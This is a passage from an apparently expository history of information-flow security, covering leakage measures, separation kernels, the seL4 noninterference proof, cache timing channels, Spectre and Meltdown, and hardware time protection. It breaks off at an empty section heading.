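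In 2009 Geoffrey Smith proposed min-entropy leakage, which measures how much an output helps an attacker who has one guess at the secret:

min-entropy leakage = log₂(chance of a correct guess after seeing the output / chance before)

The attacker always makes the best available guess, and the chance afterwards is an average over all possible outputs. The two measures can differ greatly:

| System | Shannon leakage | Chance of a correct guess, before and after | Min-entropy leakage |
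|---|---|---|---|
| Sends a fair bit correctly 99% of the time | 0.92 bits | 1/2, then 0.99 | 0.99 bits |
| Outputs 0, 1 or a fair bit, each a third of the time | 0.08 bits | 1/2, then 2/3 | 0.42 bits |
| Prints a 64-bit key one time in eight | 8 bits | 2⁻⁶⁴, then about 1/8 | about 61 bits |
| Always prints the first 16 bits of a 64-bit key | 16 bits | 2⁻⁶⁴, then 2⁻⁴⁸ | 16 bits |
| Sends a bit that is 1 nine times in ten, correctly 80% of the time | 0.10 bits | 0.9, then 0.9 | 0 bits |

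The measures rank the two 64-bit systems in opposite orders. Min-entropy leakage is more relevant for a key that an attacker can use immediately. Shannon capacity is more informative about a Trojan horse that can encode a long message and use a channel many times.

Min-entropy leakage can also miss a leak. In the last row, the attacker's best guess is 1 before seeing any output and remains 1 even after an output of 0. The measure is therefore zero, although the output changes the probabilities and the system violates probabilistic noninterference.

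The figures in the table also apply only to a single run. If the system that prints the key one time in eight makes a fresh choice each time, an attacker who runs it twenty times has a 93% chance of getting the key. Clarkson and Schneider account for repeated use by formalising the requirement that a program leak less than k bits over every series of experiments.

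## Certified separation kernels and the proof of seL4, 1999 to 2026

Rushby wanted a separation kernel to make one processor behave like several separate machines. By the late 1990s aircraft designers wanted the same thing, mainly for safety and cost reasons.

### Partitioning in aircraft computers

Airliners traditionally gave each automatic function, such as the autopilot or the flight management system, its own computer system. In *Partitioning in Avionics Architectures*, a report for NASA and the US Federal Aviation Administration, Rushby (1999) called this a federated architecture. It naturally limits the spread of faults because the functions share very little, and designers can build each function to tolerate bad data from the others. It is also wasteful. The major functions of a large airliner could use as many as 50 processors, yet one faulty processor might prevent takeoff because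 no processor could take over another function's work.

Rushby argued that the federated design had a safety drawback too. An aircraft's thrust and pitch affect each other, but the autothrottle controlled thrust and the autopilot controlled pitch, with no higher-level system to coordinate them. Manufacturers added special modes to deal with the conflicts. Rushby thought this complexity caused some of the pilot confusion about automation that investigators had linked to fatal crashes.

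The alternative, integrated modular avionics, runs several functions on a shared computer system. A faulty function could monopolise the processor, corrupt another function's memory or send commands to its actuators, which move parts of the aircraft. Partitioning has to restore the protection that separate computers gave. It addresses only the hazards that sharing adds, so it does not protect a function from the failure of its processor. A function with its own computer would be just as vulnerable to that failure, and only replicated hardware protects against it.

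Engineers divide isolation into space partitioning, which stops one function from changing another's memory or controlling its devices, and time partitioning, which stops one function from taking processor time that another needs. The SUE, the British kernel of the early 1980s, had only space partitioning, which would be unacceptable in a computer that runs both a weather radar and an autopilot.

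Partitioning also reduces the cost of certification. Under DO-178B, the guidelines for airborne software at the time, the strictest level, Level A, applied to software whose malfunction could contribute to a catastrophic failure. Without partitioning, a minor program that shares a processor with Level A software must also meet Level A, because a fault in it could affect that software. Partitioning lets developers certify each program to the level its own importance requires. Rushby added that this could make aircraft safer, since the cost of Level A discouraged designers from including useful extras such as continuous self-tests.

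Partitions that run on top of a complete operating system rely on a great deal of its software to keep them separate. Running them on a minimal kernel, with separate operating system services inside each partition, reduces that reliance to the kernel and the hardware.

ARINC 653 is the aviation industry's standard for the interface between such a system and its applications. A fixed, repeating timetable gives each partition set windows of processor time. For example, a 100-millisecond cycle might give the autopilot the first 40 milliseconds and the radar the next 20, whether or not either has work to do. Partitions exchange messages through ports that the system's integrator sets up in advance. Rapita Systems, a company that sells testing tools for avionics software, warns that compliance with ARINC 653 does not guarantee robust partitioning. The standard defines the interface and what partitioning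 should do, but not how to show that a particular system does it.

DiVito (1998) adapted mathematical models from computer security to state the requirements for partitioning in avionics, and tested the approach on three designs simplified from real systems. Noninterference suits this purpose because it rules out unwanted influence of any kind, whether from a spy's program or from a function that corrupts another's data.

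### MILS and the Greve-Wilding-Vanfleet property

Military suppliers adopted the same architecture under the name MILS ("multiple independent levels of security"). In *A Separation Kernel Formal Security Policy*, Greve and Wilding (2003) explain that MILS splits the design of a secure system into two smaller problems. One team builds and verifies a separation kernel. Others build applications that rely on the kernel's protection and enforce sensible policies of their own, the same division Rushby made between separation and mediation.

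*A High Assurance Partitioned Development Environment* (2003) describes how Rockwell Collins, an avionics manufacturer, was building partitioning into the hardware of the AAMP7 processor. Greve and Wilding, who worked there, wanted a property that a kernel's developers could prove and that application developers could use in their own proofs. It became known as the Greve-Wilding-Vanfleet property, or GWV, because Mark Vanfleet co-authored the version published later that year.

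The property describes a machine whose memory consists of named segments:

- segs(p) is the set of segments that belong to partition p.
- current(s) is the partition that is running in state s.
- select(x, s) is the value of segment x in state s.
- next(s) is the state after one step of the machine.
- dia(x) is the set of segments that may directly affect segment x. This is the flow policy.

When the machine takes a step, the new value of a segment x may depend only on its old value and on those segments of the running partition that may affect x. In symbols, let D = dia(x) ∩ segs(current(s)). Then for all segments x and all states s and t:

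current(s) = current(t), select(x, s) = select(x, t), and select(y, s) = select(y, t) for every y in D ⇒ select(x, next(s)) = select(x, next(t))

Other researchers had proposed several separate requirements for separation kernels, and Greve and Wilding proved that three of these follow from their single property:

- No exfiltration: if the running partition has no segment that may affect x, the new value of x depends only on its old value.
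- Mediation: the new value of any segment depends only on its old value and on the segments of the running partition.
- No infiltration: the new value of a segment that belongs to the running partition depends only on that partition's segments.

GWV resembles Rushby's conditions for intransitive policies, with the running partition as the domain that acts. It is more precise because it applies to segments, so a policy can let one partition write to another's inbox but not to its program. GWV is more permissive than Rushby's local respect because it allows a segment to change on its own, as a clock does.

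However, GWV alone does not restrict how the kernel chooses the next partition. Suppose the kernel runs B right after A if A's secret bit is 1, but runs C before B if the bit is 0. Each step can satisfy GWV, but B can learn the bit by checking a clock when its turn comes. Greve and Wilding suggested ruling out this leak by assuming that only the kernel's record of the current partition can affect that record.

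To test whether application developers could use the property, they proved that a simple firewall works. Partition b must never contain sensitive data, and partition f, the firewall, controls what b receives. The proof needs three main assumptions:

- No partition other than b itself can affect b's segments, except that f can write to one of them, called the outbox.
- While f is running, it never puts sensitive data into an outbox that contains none.
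- If no segment of the machine contains sensitive data, no segment contains any after the next step. Decryption keys must therefore count as sensitive, since otherwise a program could produce secrets from harmless data.

The theorem is that if b starts without sensitive data, it never contains any. The proof compares one step of the real machine with the same step of an imaginary machine in which all the sensitive data outside b has first been erased. The imaginary machine starts the step with no sensitive data, so by the third assumption it has none afterward. By GWV, the step has the same effect on b in both machines, because nothing outside b affects its segments. The only exception is the outbox while f is running, which the second assumption covers. So b still contains no sensitive data after the step in the real machine, and the same argument applies to each later step.

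The second assumption matters most. It concerns the firewall's own program and needs a separate proof, as does the censor in Rushby's encryption device.

### The protection profile and INTEGRITY-178B

The Common Criteria is an international scheme for evaluating product security. A protection profile lists the requirements for one type of product. In June 2007, the US National Security Agency published version 1.03 of a profile for separation kernels "in Environments Requiring High Robustness". The scheme's American branch certified INTEGRITY-178B, a real-time operating system from Green Hills Software, against this profile in 2008. The certificate covered one version of the kernel on one model of PowerPC board.

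The agency withdrew the profile in 2011 because a kernel's conformance did not by itself give enough confidence that the larger system built on it would protect national security information. Rushby's design had implied this, since it left the overall policy to trusted components such as the censor.

The evaluation also left a gap within the kernel. Murray, Matichuk and colleagues (2013) point out in *seL4* that even the strictest levels of the Common Criteria do not require a proof about the code that runs. INTEGRITY-178B had a machine-checked proof of information flow, based on a later version of GWV, but it applied to a detailed handwritten model. Only a careful informal argument connected this model to the code. A programming error could therefore break the isolation without affecting the proof, and the developers might change the code and forget to update the model.

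Other verified separation kernels had the same weakness:

| System | What researchers proved secure | How they connected it to the implementation |
|---|---|---|
| INTEGRITY-178B | A detailed hand-written model | Informal argument |
| MASK, the Mathematically Analyzed Separation Kernel | A low-level design | Manual translation into C |
| An unnamed kernel of about 3,000 lines for an embedded system | An abstract model | Pen-and-paper proof |
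| The AAMP7 processor | A fairly detailed model | Manual inspection of the microcode |

In *seL4*, Heiser (2026) lists INTEGRITY among several commercial microkernel systems with known critical vulnerabilities. INTEGRITY-178B belongs to that product family, but the listing does not show that the certified version had any of these vulnerabilities.

### From specification to C code

Researchers at NICTA, an Australian research institute, proved that the code of the seL4 microkernel matches its model. A microkernel provides only basic mechanisms and leaves services such as file systems and device drivers to ordinary programs. Unlike the SUE or MASK, seL4 was designed for general use, but its developers showed that system designers can configure it as a separation kernel.

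Programs on seL4 can use a kernel object, such as a thread or a page of memory, only if they hold a capability for it. When the system starts, one initial thread holds all the capabilities. It creates the partitions, gives each the capabilities it needs, and then destroys itself. The proof of information flow applies from then on. Traditional separation kernels typically accept no further requests once this configuration is complete, whereas a program inside an seL4 partition can still create threads and allocate memory. A partition can also run a modified Linux.

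The seL4 kernel keeps no common pool of memory for creating objects. Heiser explains that a program must use its own share of memory for any object the kernel creates on its behalf. One partition therefore cannot use up memory that another needs. In Rushby's toy kernel, partitions could signal to each other by doing this.

The security proof rests on two earlier ones. The first, which the team completed in 2009, established functional correctness, meaning that the C code does only what the abstract specification allows. The specification describes the kernel as a state machine, in 4,970 lines of logic written for the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL. If execution(M, s, α) is the set of states that machine M can reach from state s through the sequence of transitions α, the theorem is:

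execution(C code, s, α) ⊆ execution(specification, s, α) for all s and α

The seL4 proof shows refinement in the sense used for nondeterministic systems. Murray and colleagues estimate that it took around 25 person-years. Heiser gives 11 person-years, excluding the work on frameworks that other projects could reuse.

The second proof, from 2011, established integrity. A running thread can change the system only in ways that its capabilities authorise, and no thread can gain more authority than the configuration allows. The team proved this for the specification and used refinement to extend the result to the C code. The proof took only 10 person-months.

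Integrity restricts only what a partition can change. To show that the kernel also restricts what a partition can learn, Murray and colleagues needed a proof of noninterference, and they wanted it to cover the kernel's 8,830 lines of C.

### The information-flow theorem

The threat model assumes that all code outside the kernel becomes malicious once the system has started, and that the malicious programs cooperate. The attackers know the code and configuration of the whole system, including the kernel, and may execute any instruction or make any request to the kernel. They do not know what other partitions contain, and they try to learn what the policy forbids. The model also assumes a physically secure computer with one processor and trustworthy hardware.

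The flow policy follows from the capabilities that the initial thread hands out. For each partition, Murray and colleagues first work out which partitions' data it can learn about directly. Partition A may influence partition B if A can change anything that B can learn about directly. For example, if P2 can read a page of P1's memory, then P1 may influence P2, and so may any other partition that can write to P1's memory.

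The scheduler counts as a separate partition. It runs the other partitions in a fixed rotation with fixed time slices, and chooses freely only among the threads inside the current partition. It may influence every partition, because it decides when each one runs, but no partition may influence it. Otherwise, information could flow between any two partitions through the scheduler. This condition also rules out the scheduling leak that GWV allows.

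Murray and colleagues used nonleakage, a variant of intransitive noninterference that von Oheimb had introduced and that protects what partitions contain. They did not use a purge because a fixed, public schedule already reveals when each partition runs, so there is no point in hiding that its actions took place. Nonleakage compares two system states that have the same scheduler data and the same contents in every partition that may legitimately send information to a partition p, directly or through permitted intermediaries, during the next n steps. After n steps from each state, the contents of p must also be the same.

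As usual, the proof uses a condition on single steps. Let view(p, s) be everything that partition p can learn about directly in state s, let r be the partition that is running, and let s′ and t′ be any states that can follow s and t. For all partitions p and all reachable states s and t:

view(p, s) = view(p, t), view(scheduler, s) = view(scheduler, t) and, if r ⇝ p, view(r, s) = view(r, t) ⇒ view(p, s′) = view(p, t′)

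This is close to Rushby's weak step consistency, with the scheduler added. Murray and colleagues had shown that it is equivalent to nonleakage. The proof for seL4 has three main cases:

- If r must not influence p and p is an ordinary partition, the integrity theorem already guarantees that r's step does not change anything p can see.
- If p is the scheduler, the proof has to show that its data do not depend on what the running partition does.
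- If r may influence p, the proof has to show that the kernel reveals only data that the policy allows. This case took most of the work.

The scheduler case required a change to the kernel model. The kernel checks for interrupts at certain points during long requests, and in the model each check advances a counter that partitions can use as a coarse clock. The number of checks depends on the data in the request, so another partition could learn about that data from the counter. In reality, no other partition can read the counter until its own turn begins. Murray and colleagues therefore treated everything a partition does between two timer ticks as a single step, after which the counter always stands at the next tick.

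The ARM version of seL4 keeps one page of memory that all threads share and fills it with data about the running thread. As with Rushby's SWAP operation, the proof had to show that nothing from the previous partition remains in that page or in the processor's registers after a switch between partitions.

Nonleakage carries over to the C code by refinement, but only because it rules out all nondeterminism that a program can observe. The original specification left some observable choices open, and in several places the C code made them using internal data that the specification did not mention, any of which could have been a storage channel. The team made the specification more precise and repaired the earlier proofs to match.

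This took about 23 of the project's 51 person-months. The security proof took about 26, and the new scheduler about 2. The finished information flow proof has 27,756 lines. Murray and colleagues estimated that proving the property directly on the C code would have taken more than 25 person-years.

### Restrictions on what partitions may share

Apart from adding the scheduler and making one minor change to simplify verification, the team did not have to alter the kernel's code. But several of its ordinary features carry information in directions that a designer might not expect. Murray and colleagues dealt with these by restricting how partitions may be connected:

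- Synchronous messages make the sender wait until the receiver is ready, so the sender learns something about the receiver. If two partitions are connected in this way, the policy has to allow information to flow in both directions. The proof shows that nobody else learns anything from the exchange.
- A partition must not pass capabilities to another, because the receiver's authority could then exceed what the configuration allows.
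- The kernel does not isolate one partition's interrupts from another's. All interrupts except the timer's therefore stay disabled, and device drivers have to check their devices repeatedly for new data.
- A channel between partitions must last as long as the system runs. seL4 deletes an object when somebody deletes the last capability for it, so a partition that deletes a capability could find out whether another partition still holds one. To prevent this, the initial thread stores a spare copy of every capability that crosses a partition boundary in a place that no partition can reach.

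The channel through deletion surprised even people who had worked on seL4 for years. It also shows that a proof can reveal leaks that a list of known ones, like Lampson's, might miss.

Components can still communicate in one direction through shared memory that only one side can write to, and through asynchronous notifications, which never make the sender wait. Notifications were among the hardest parts of the project to prove safe, because the kernel has to examine the state of the receiving end to deliver one. The team had to show that the result looks the same to the sender whatever that state is.

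### What the proof assumes

The theorem also depends on things that the proof does not examine. In 2013 these included the following:

- The compiler and linker translate the C code correctly.
- About 450 lines of assembly code, and the code that starts the kernel, are correct.
- The hardware behaves as the formal model predicts.
- No device uses direct memory access, which the SUE also excluded, because a device could otherwise write over the kernel's memory.
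- The system uses one processor.
- Partitions may know the schedule and observe the passage of time.
- Partitions cannot communicate through external devices.

The model does not represent how long operations take, so the proof does not rule out timing channels. Murray and colleagues listed several that certainly existed, including shared caches and a partition's ability to overrun its time slice by making a request just before the slice ends.

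The project has since removed one of the largest assumptions, that the compiled program matches the C code. A separate automatic tool can now check this. *The seL4 verification project*, by Trustworthy Systems, the research group that created seL4, reports that the check covers ARMv7 and 64-bit RISC-V processors.

Most of the other assumptions remain. The seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume* lists about 340 lines of ARM assembly, 1,200 lines of startup code, and the operations that manage the processor's caches. It also states that the treatment of virtual memory, the hardware mechanism that keeps programs in their own areas of memory, leaves some room for human error. Virtual memory can affect the kernel's own memory accesses, and the prover does not check that the team has identified every condition needed to prevent problems.

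### Attacks on drones and a helicopter

From 2012 to 2017, DARPA, the US military's research agency, tested seL4 and other verified software on real vehicles in its High-Assurance Cyber Military Systems (HACMS) programme. According to Trustworthy Systems' *Multicore seL4 Verification*, a DARPA-funded project put seL4 and a small real-time system called eChronos into autonomous aircraft. The HACMS vehicles included a quadcopter and Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a full-sized helicopter that can fly without a pilot.

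In 2015 a red team, a group hired to attack the system, had six weeks to take over the helicopter's computers. The team started with control of the partition that ran the camera, but could not break out of it or disrupt the rest of the system. In February 2017 the helicopter flew with a safety pilot on board while rogue camera software and a virus from a USB stick attacked its mission computer. The attacks compromised some subsystems but did not affect flight safety. Heiser adds that DARPA invited hackers at the 2021 DEF CON conference to "steal this drone", and that nobody compromised the seL4-based system.

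Giving the red team a partition to start from made the test realistic, because the purpose of separation is to contain a component that has already failed. But Anderson's 1972 warning about tiger teams still applies, since whether an attack succeeds depends on the attackers' skill and time. The trials mainly tested whether attackers could disrupt the flight, which concerns integrity and availability, so they provide much less evidence that secrets cannot leak from one partition to another.

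seL4 has since gone into commercial products, including electric cars from the Chinese manufacturer NIO. Heiser acknowledges that it is hard to use because it provides no file system, networking or device drivers. Most successful deployments so far have involved either its creators or companies that hired several graduates of their university.

### Coverage in 2026

Each version of seL4 for a different processor needs its own proof, and some features have none. The table combines the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations* with later announcements in its *seL4 News*.

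| Configuration | Functional correctness | Information flow |
|---|---|---|
| ARMv7 (Sabre Lite board) | Proved | Proved |
| 64-bit RISC-V (HiFive board) | Proved | Proved |
| 64-bit ARM, with support for virtual machines | Proved | Proved in 2026 |
| ARMv7, with support for virtual machines | Proved | Not proved |
| 64-bit x86 | Proved | Not proved |
| Real-time extensions on RISC-V | Proved in 2026 | Not proved |
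| Several processor cores | Not proved | Not proved |

Proofcraft, a company founded by the leaders of the verification work, completed the newest proof, for 64-bit ARM, in the second half of 2026. seL4 still has no information-flow proof for the x86 processors common in servers and desktop computers. None of the proofs covers the hardware that restricts which memory a device can reach, so they do not fully cover a system that relies on such hardware to allow direct memory access safely.

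According to the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs*, confidentiality holds between the partitions of the fixed schedule and not between arbitrary threads, even in the configurations with a complete proof.

The restriction to one core is perhaps the most important in practice, because most modern processors have several. *seL4 Multikernel Roadmap and Concurrency Verification* (Lewis, 2024) gives it as a footnote to the claim that seL4 is the world's most highly assured kernel. On several cores, parts of the kernel can run at the same time and could interact in ways the existing proofs do not cover. The team is now developing a multikernel, which runs a separate copy of the kernel on each core. The seL4 Foundation's *Development Roadmap* schedules that project for completion in the third quarter of 2028.

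Experience so far suggests that it matters which code the proofs cover. According to the seL4 Foundation, nobody has found a functional correctness defect in the verified code since 2009, while every class of unverified code has had some. The Foundation's *seL4 Version 13.0.0 Release* (2024) reports a fault that let a program crash the kernel in a multicore configuration. Its *seL4 Version 14.0.0 Release* (2025) reports another crash, in the unverified support for virtual machines on x86.

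Verified configurations can also contain defects where the proofs' assumptions are false. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Version 16.0.0 Release* (2026) describes two such defects. One allowed a program on ARMv7 with the right capabilities to crash the whole system by requesting a cache operation on memory that was no longer in use. It affected all previous versions, including the configuration with the information-flow proof. The proofs did not rule it out because they assume that cache operations work correctly.

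The other defect affected ARM configurations that support virtual machines. The kernel did not handle one processor register properly when it switched between threads, so one guest operating system could overwrite a value that another was about to read. Murray and colleagues had warned of something similar in 2013, when they described a hypothetical version of seL4 for a new processor with extra registers that the kernel never reads and does not clear when it switches partitions. The proof could still hold, even though the registers would be an obvious storage channel.

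Verified configurations include some code that the proofs do not cover. The developers audited this code for version 17.0.0, later in 2026, and fixed a number of problems in it and in unverified configurations. The AI company Anthropic had reported some of these problems.

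## Timing channels, 2014 to 2026

The 2013 proof of seL4 does not cover timing channels because, as Trustworthy Systems explains, its model leaves out time. A processor's instruction set, the published description of what each instruction does, also leaves out time. It defines which value a program gets when it reads from memory, but not whether that value comes from main memory or from a cache, a small, fast store that holds copies of recently used data. Hardware designers treat caches as internal details because they change a program's speed but never its results. Partitions that take turns on a processor share its caches.

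Other shared parts of a processor have the same effect. The translation lookaside buffer, or TLB, holds recent translations of virtual memory addresses into physical ones. Branch predictors use the outcomes of earlier branches to predict which way a program will go next, and prefetchers fetch data that a program seems likely to need soon. One partition can leave state in any of these that speeds up or slows down the next partition. The buses between processor cores and memory keep no such state, but programs running at the same time on different cores compete for them, and each can detect when the other's traffic slows its own.

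### How a shared cache carries a message

Suppose High and Low take turns on a processor whose cache has eight lines, each holding one block of memory. Reading a block takes 10 cycles if it is in the cache and 100 if it is not. Low fills the cache with eight blocks of its own. On its next turn, it reads all eight again and measures the total time.

If High has left the cache alone, Low's accesses to its eight blocks take 80 cycles. If High's own memory accesses have displaced three of those blocks, they take 5 × 10 + 3 × 100 = 350 cycles. Each displaced block adds 90 cycles, so High can produce eight different durations by displacing between zero and seven blocks, enough to send 3 bits. If a round takes 3 milliseconds, High can send about 333 messages a second, or 1,000 bits per second, without either program reading or writing anything that belongs to the other.

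A real cache has thousands of lines, and the measurements contain noise, so researchers have to measure the leak rate experimentally. When the sender cooperates, as High does here, the leak is a covert channel. In a side channel, the sender is a victim whose normal operation leaks information, for example when an encryption program's memory accesses depend on its key. Side channels usually carry much less information than covert channels, but a key is short enough that they can still leak one.

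### Measurements on seL4 in 2014

In *The Last Mile* (2014), Cock, Ge and colleagues measured a cache channel of this kind on seL4, using six processors released between 2005 and 2012. They collected about 2,000 hours of observations over a year. On the newest chip, each observation carried about 7 bits, which at 333 observations a second gives about 2,400 bits per second.

Lampson and Rushby had both mentioned noise as a remedy, but Cock and colleagues calculated that the amount of random noise required grows without limit as the permitted channel capacity approaches zero. They tested two countermeasures that reduce the signal instead.

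Instruction-based scheduling stops a receiver from using the length of its turn as a clock. The kernel normally switches partitions after a fixed time, so a receiver can detect cache misses by counting how much work it completes in each turn. If the kernel instead switches after a fixed number of instructions, cache misses lengthen the turn but don't change the amount of work completed. This helps only if the receiver has no other source of time, such as a network connection.

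Cache colouring divides a cache between partitions. In most large caches, a block's physical address determines which group of lines can hold it. Operating systems allocate memory in pages, typically of 4 KiB, and two pages whose addresses differ in certain bits can never occupy the same lines. Pages that can occupy the same lines have the same "colour". The number of colours is the cache size divided by the product of the page size and the number of lines in each group. A 1 MiB cache with 4 KiB pages and 16 lines per group therefore has 1,024 / (4 × 16) = 16 colours. If the kernel never gives two partitions pages of the same colour, neither can displace the other's data from the cache.

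| Processor and year of release | No countermeasure (bits/s) | Instruction-based scheduling (bits/s) | Cache colouring (bits/s) |
|---|---|---|---|
| iMX.31 (Arm), 2005 | 1,400 | 0.1 | 7.1 |
| E6550 (Intel), 2007 | 1,500 | 9.5 | 76 |
| DM3730 (Arm), 2010 | 1,800 | 0.5 | 1.7 |
| AM3358 (Arm), 2011 | 1,600 | 0.6 | 5.0 |
| iMX.6 (Arm), 2011 | 2,100 | Not measured | 12 |
| Exynos4412 (Arm), 2012 | 2,400 | 400 | 27 |

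Both methods worked well on simple processors and worse on complex ones. Instruction-based scheduling nearly failed on the Exynos4412 because that chip does not interrupt a program exactly at the chosen instruction. It seems to wait for a pause in the flow of instructions, and cache misses affect when that pause occurs.

Small but real leaks remained under cache colouring. A finite sample can make a channel with no capacity appear to have some, so Cock and colleagues simulated 1,000 zero-capacity channels for each experiment and used the highest apparent rate as a threshold. Every figure in the colouring column is above its threshold. On the Exynos4412, part of the leak came from competition for the TLB, which colouring does not divide. Clearing the TLB at every switch reduced the rate from 27 to 25 bits per second, but Cock and colleagues could not find the source of the rest. At 25 bits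 per second, a 1,024-bit key leaks in about 41 seconds.

They also found a previously unreported channel. On the AM3358, the cycle counter seems to miss a cycle whenever the processor mispredicts a branch. A receiver that compared this counter with the kernel's regular timer could learn about the sender's branches at 1,100 bits per second. Giving each partition its own virtual counter closes the channel.

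Another experiment involved a remote attacker, whose access to a clock no kernel can block. A version of OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, took slightly different times to reject two specially altered packets. An attacker in Oregon could tell with over 60% accuracy, after a single observation, which of the two a server in Sydney had received, compared with 50% by guessing. OpenSSL's developers had already rewritten the code to run in constant time, but on an Arm processor an attacker on a neighbouring machine could still guess correctly 62% of the time. Using seL4 to hold every reply until a scheduled time reduced this to 57% and gave faster replies than the rewritten code.

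### Spectre and Meltdown

Spectre and Meltdown, two attacks that researchers disclosed in January 2018, made it hard for designers to keep regarding covert channels as a problem only for systems that might contain a Trojan horse. Both exploit speculative or out-of-order execution, in which a processor executes instructions before confirming that they should run. If some should not have run, the processor discards their results. This leaves registers and memory unchanged, but the data those instructions loaded remains in the cache.

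In Spectre, the attacker manipulates the branch predictor so that a victim program briefly runs instructions that its own checks should have prevented. These instructions leave a trace in the cache that depends on a secret. In Meltdown, the attacker's own program briefly uses data from the kernel's memory before the processor acts on the failed permission check. The processor never returns the forbidden value to the program, but the program can recover it from the cache.

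The proofs about seL4 assume that the hardware enforces memory protection, but Meltdown showed that a processor can enforce it on a program's results and still leak the contents of protected memory. Spectre weakened the assumption that a trusted component contains no Trojan horse. Ge, Yarom and colleagues (2019) explain in *Time Protection* that the attack builds one out of pieces of the victim's own code. A trusted component, such as the censor in Rushby's encryption device, might therefore send signals through the cache even if its program is correct.

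Programmers who write encryption software had long used constant-time programming, which keeps secrets from influencing a program's branches and memory addresses. According to *Granite* (2026), Spectre, Meltdown and the many attacks that followed invalidated the hardware assumptions behind this method.

### Time protection

Memory protection is mandatory, meaning the kernel enforces it whether or not programs cooperate. Ge and colleagues proposed a counterpart for timing called time protection, a collection of kernel mechanisms that keep one partition's activity from affecting another's speed. They implemented it in an experimental version of seL4 and tested it on an Intel processor and an older Arm one.

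Cache colouring divides the larger caches, including those that several cores share. To test it, Ge and colleagues repeated a known attack in which a spy program on one core monitors a program on another core as it decrypts a file. The spy program could detect each squaring operation, and the intervals between them revealed the key. With the cache divided by colour, it could no longer detect these operations.

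Colouring the partitions' memory does not separate the kernel's code, which all partitions use. A sender could make different system calls that brought different parts of the kernel into the cache, and a receiver recovered 0.79 bits every 2 milliseconds, or 395 bits per second. Ge and colleagues therefore gave each partition its own copy of the kernel, in memory of that partition's colours. The leak fell to 0.0006 bits, which is below what their tools could reliably detect. Making a copy took 79 microseconds on the Intel processor, less than a third of the time Linux needs to start a process. The copies still share about 9.5 KiB of data per core, such as the scheduler's queues. The kernel loads all of this data into the cache before each switch ends, so its presence there reveals nothing.

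The smallest caches, the TLB and the branch predictors usually cannot be coloured, so the kernel has to flush them whenever it switches partitions. The Intel processor had no usable instruction for flushing only its smallest caches, so the kernel had to fill them with its own data and run through a long chain of jumps, which took about 26 microseconds. Ge and colleagues estimated that proper instructions would take about 1 microsecond.

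Flushing also creates a channel, because a cache must copy modified data back to memory before discarding it. The more data the sender has modified, the longer the switch takes. On the Arm processor this leaked 1.4 bits per observation. The kernel therefore pads each switch by waiting until a fixed time has passed since the timer interrupt. The fixed time must cover the slowest possible switch, and Ge and colleagues used about 60 microseconds. With padding, their measurements were consistent with no leak, though one Arm measurement was so noisy that a channel with no capacity could have appeared to carry 0.24 bits.

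Finally, a partition could set a device timer to go off during another partition's turn, and the interruption carried 0.9 bits per turn. Time protection assigns each device interrupt to a partition and blocks it while other partitions run, whereas the 2013 proof required all device interrupts to be disabled.

The table gives the leakage between partitions that take turns on one core, in thousandths of a bit per observation. The last column is the highest value consistent with no leak.

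| Processor | Shared component | Unprotected | Time protection | Consistent with no leak |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Intel | First-level data cache | 4,000 | 0.6 | 0.6 |
| Intel | TLB | 2,300 | 16.8 | 23.9 |
| Intel | Branch history | 1,000 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Intel | Second-level cache | 2,700 | 50.5 | 3.7 |
| Arm | First-level data cache | 2,000 | 30.2 | 39.7 |
| Arm | TLB | 600 | 1.9 | 2.2 |

Only the Intel second-level cache shows a definite remaining leak. Ge and colleagues traced most of it to the data prefetcher. Turning it off reduced the leak from 50.5 to 6.4, and they suspected that a second prefetcher, which they could not turn off, caused the rest. Clearing the whole cache hierarchy closed the channel but took about 270 microseconds per switch, compared with 30 for time protection.

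With turns of 10 milliseconds, a 30-microsecond switch uses about 0.3% of the processor's time. The larger slowdown comes from giving each partition only part of the cache. With half the cache and time protection with padding, standard benchmark programs ran an average of 3.4% slower on the Intel processor and 1.1% slower on the Arm one. The worst slowdowns were 11% and 7%.

These results apply to restricted settings. Ge and colleagues excluded covert channels between programs that run at the same time on different cores, because no mainstream processor could divide bus capacity between partitions. To confine a Trojan horse, a system must therefore use one core or let only one partition run at any moment. For cloud computers, where customers' programs run at the same time, they aimed to stop only side channels. They also ruled out running two partitions as simultaneous threads on a single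 core, since such threads share nearly everything. Time protection stops Spectre attacks across partition boundaries, but Meltdown requires a hardware fix.

### A fence instruction for RISC-V

The prefetcher leak illustrates the main weakness of time protection, which is that a kernel can clear only what the processor lets it clear. Researchers at ETH Zürich and the seL4 group therefore turned to RISC-V, an open instruction set that anyone may extend. *Prevention of Microarchitectural Covert Channels on an Open-Source 64-bit RISC-V Core* (2020) proposed fence.t, a "temporal fence" instruction that prevents earlier execution from affecting the timing of what runs after it.

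Deciding what the instruction should clear is difficult. In *Systematic Prevention of On-Core Timing Channels by Full Temporal Partitioning*, Wistoff, Schneider and colleagues (2022) compared three designs on CVA6, a fairly simple open-source processor. The first clears the well-known components, namely the first-level caches, the TLBs and the branch predictors. Tests of this design led Wistoff and colleagues to look for smaller components, and they found several, including the pseudo-random number generator that selects which cache line to replace and the circuits that determine which memory request goes first. The second design clears these too.

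Both designs depend on somebody having listed every component that matters, as Lampson's defence against leaks did in 1973. The third design, which Wistoff and colleagues preferred, clears everything in the core except the state that the instruction set defines, such as the registers that programs use, so the designer has to list only what to keep. If the designer forgets something, programs fail, which testers are likely to notice, whereas a component forgotten in either of the other designs leaves a silent leak.

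The instruction also pads its duration. At 1,000 switches a second on a 1 GHz processor, the overhead was 0.3% with a data cache that writes every change to memory immediately, and 2.1% with one that delays these writes and must finish them before the reset. The additional circuits increased the processor's area by 0.13%.

CVA6 executes instructions in order. Faster processors reorder them, which makes it harder to separate the state a reset should clear from the state it should keep. Such a processor may have more physical registers than the instruction set defines and keep a table of which physical register currently holds the value of each defined register. The table's contents affect timing, so the fence should clear them, but without them the processor cannot find the program's data.

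Wistoff, Heiser and Benini (2024), in *fence.t.s*, solved this with help from software. The kernel copies the official registers to memory, clears everything including the table, and then reloads the registers. They tried the method on OpenC910, an open-source commercial design. It already had instructions for clearing its caches and branch predictors, so they needed to add only one. Adding it had no noticeable effect on the chip's size or speed, but using the method slowed benchmarks by 1.0% on average. In tests of the two first-level caches and the branch history, they found large leaks without the fence and none with it. They claim that the method closes all timing channels within the core. For the components they did not report on, this claim depends on the reset being complete.

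A RISC-V task group is considering adding an instruction like fence.t to the standard, according to the project's web page, Trustworthy Systems' *Time Protection*. PlanV, a company in Munich, is to verify the circuits that implement fence.t.

### Proving time protection

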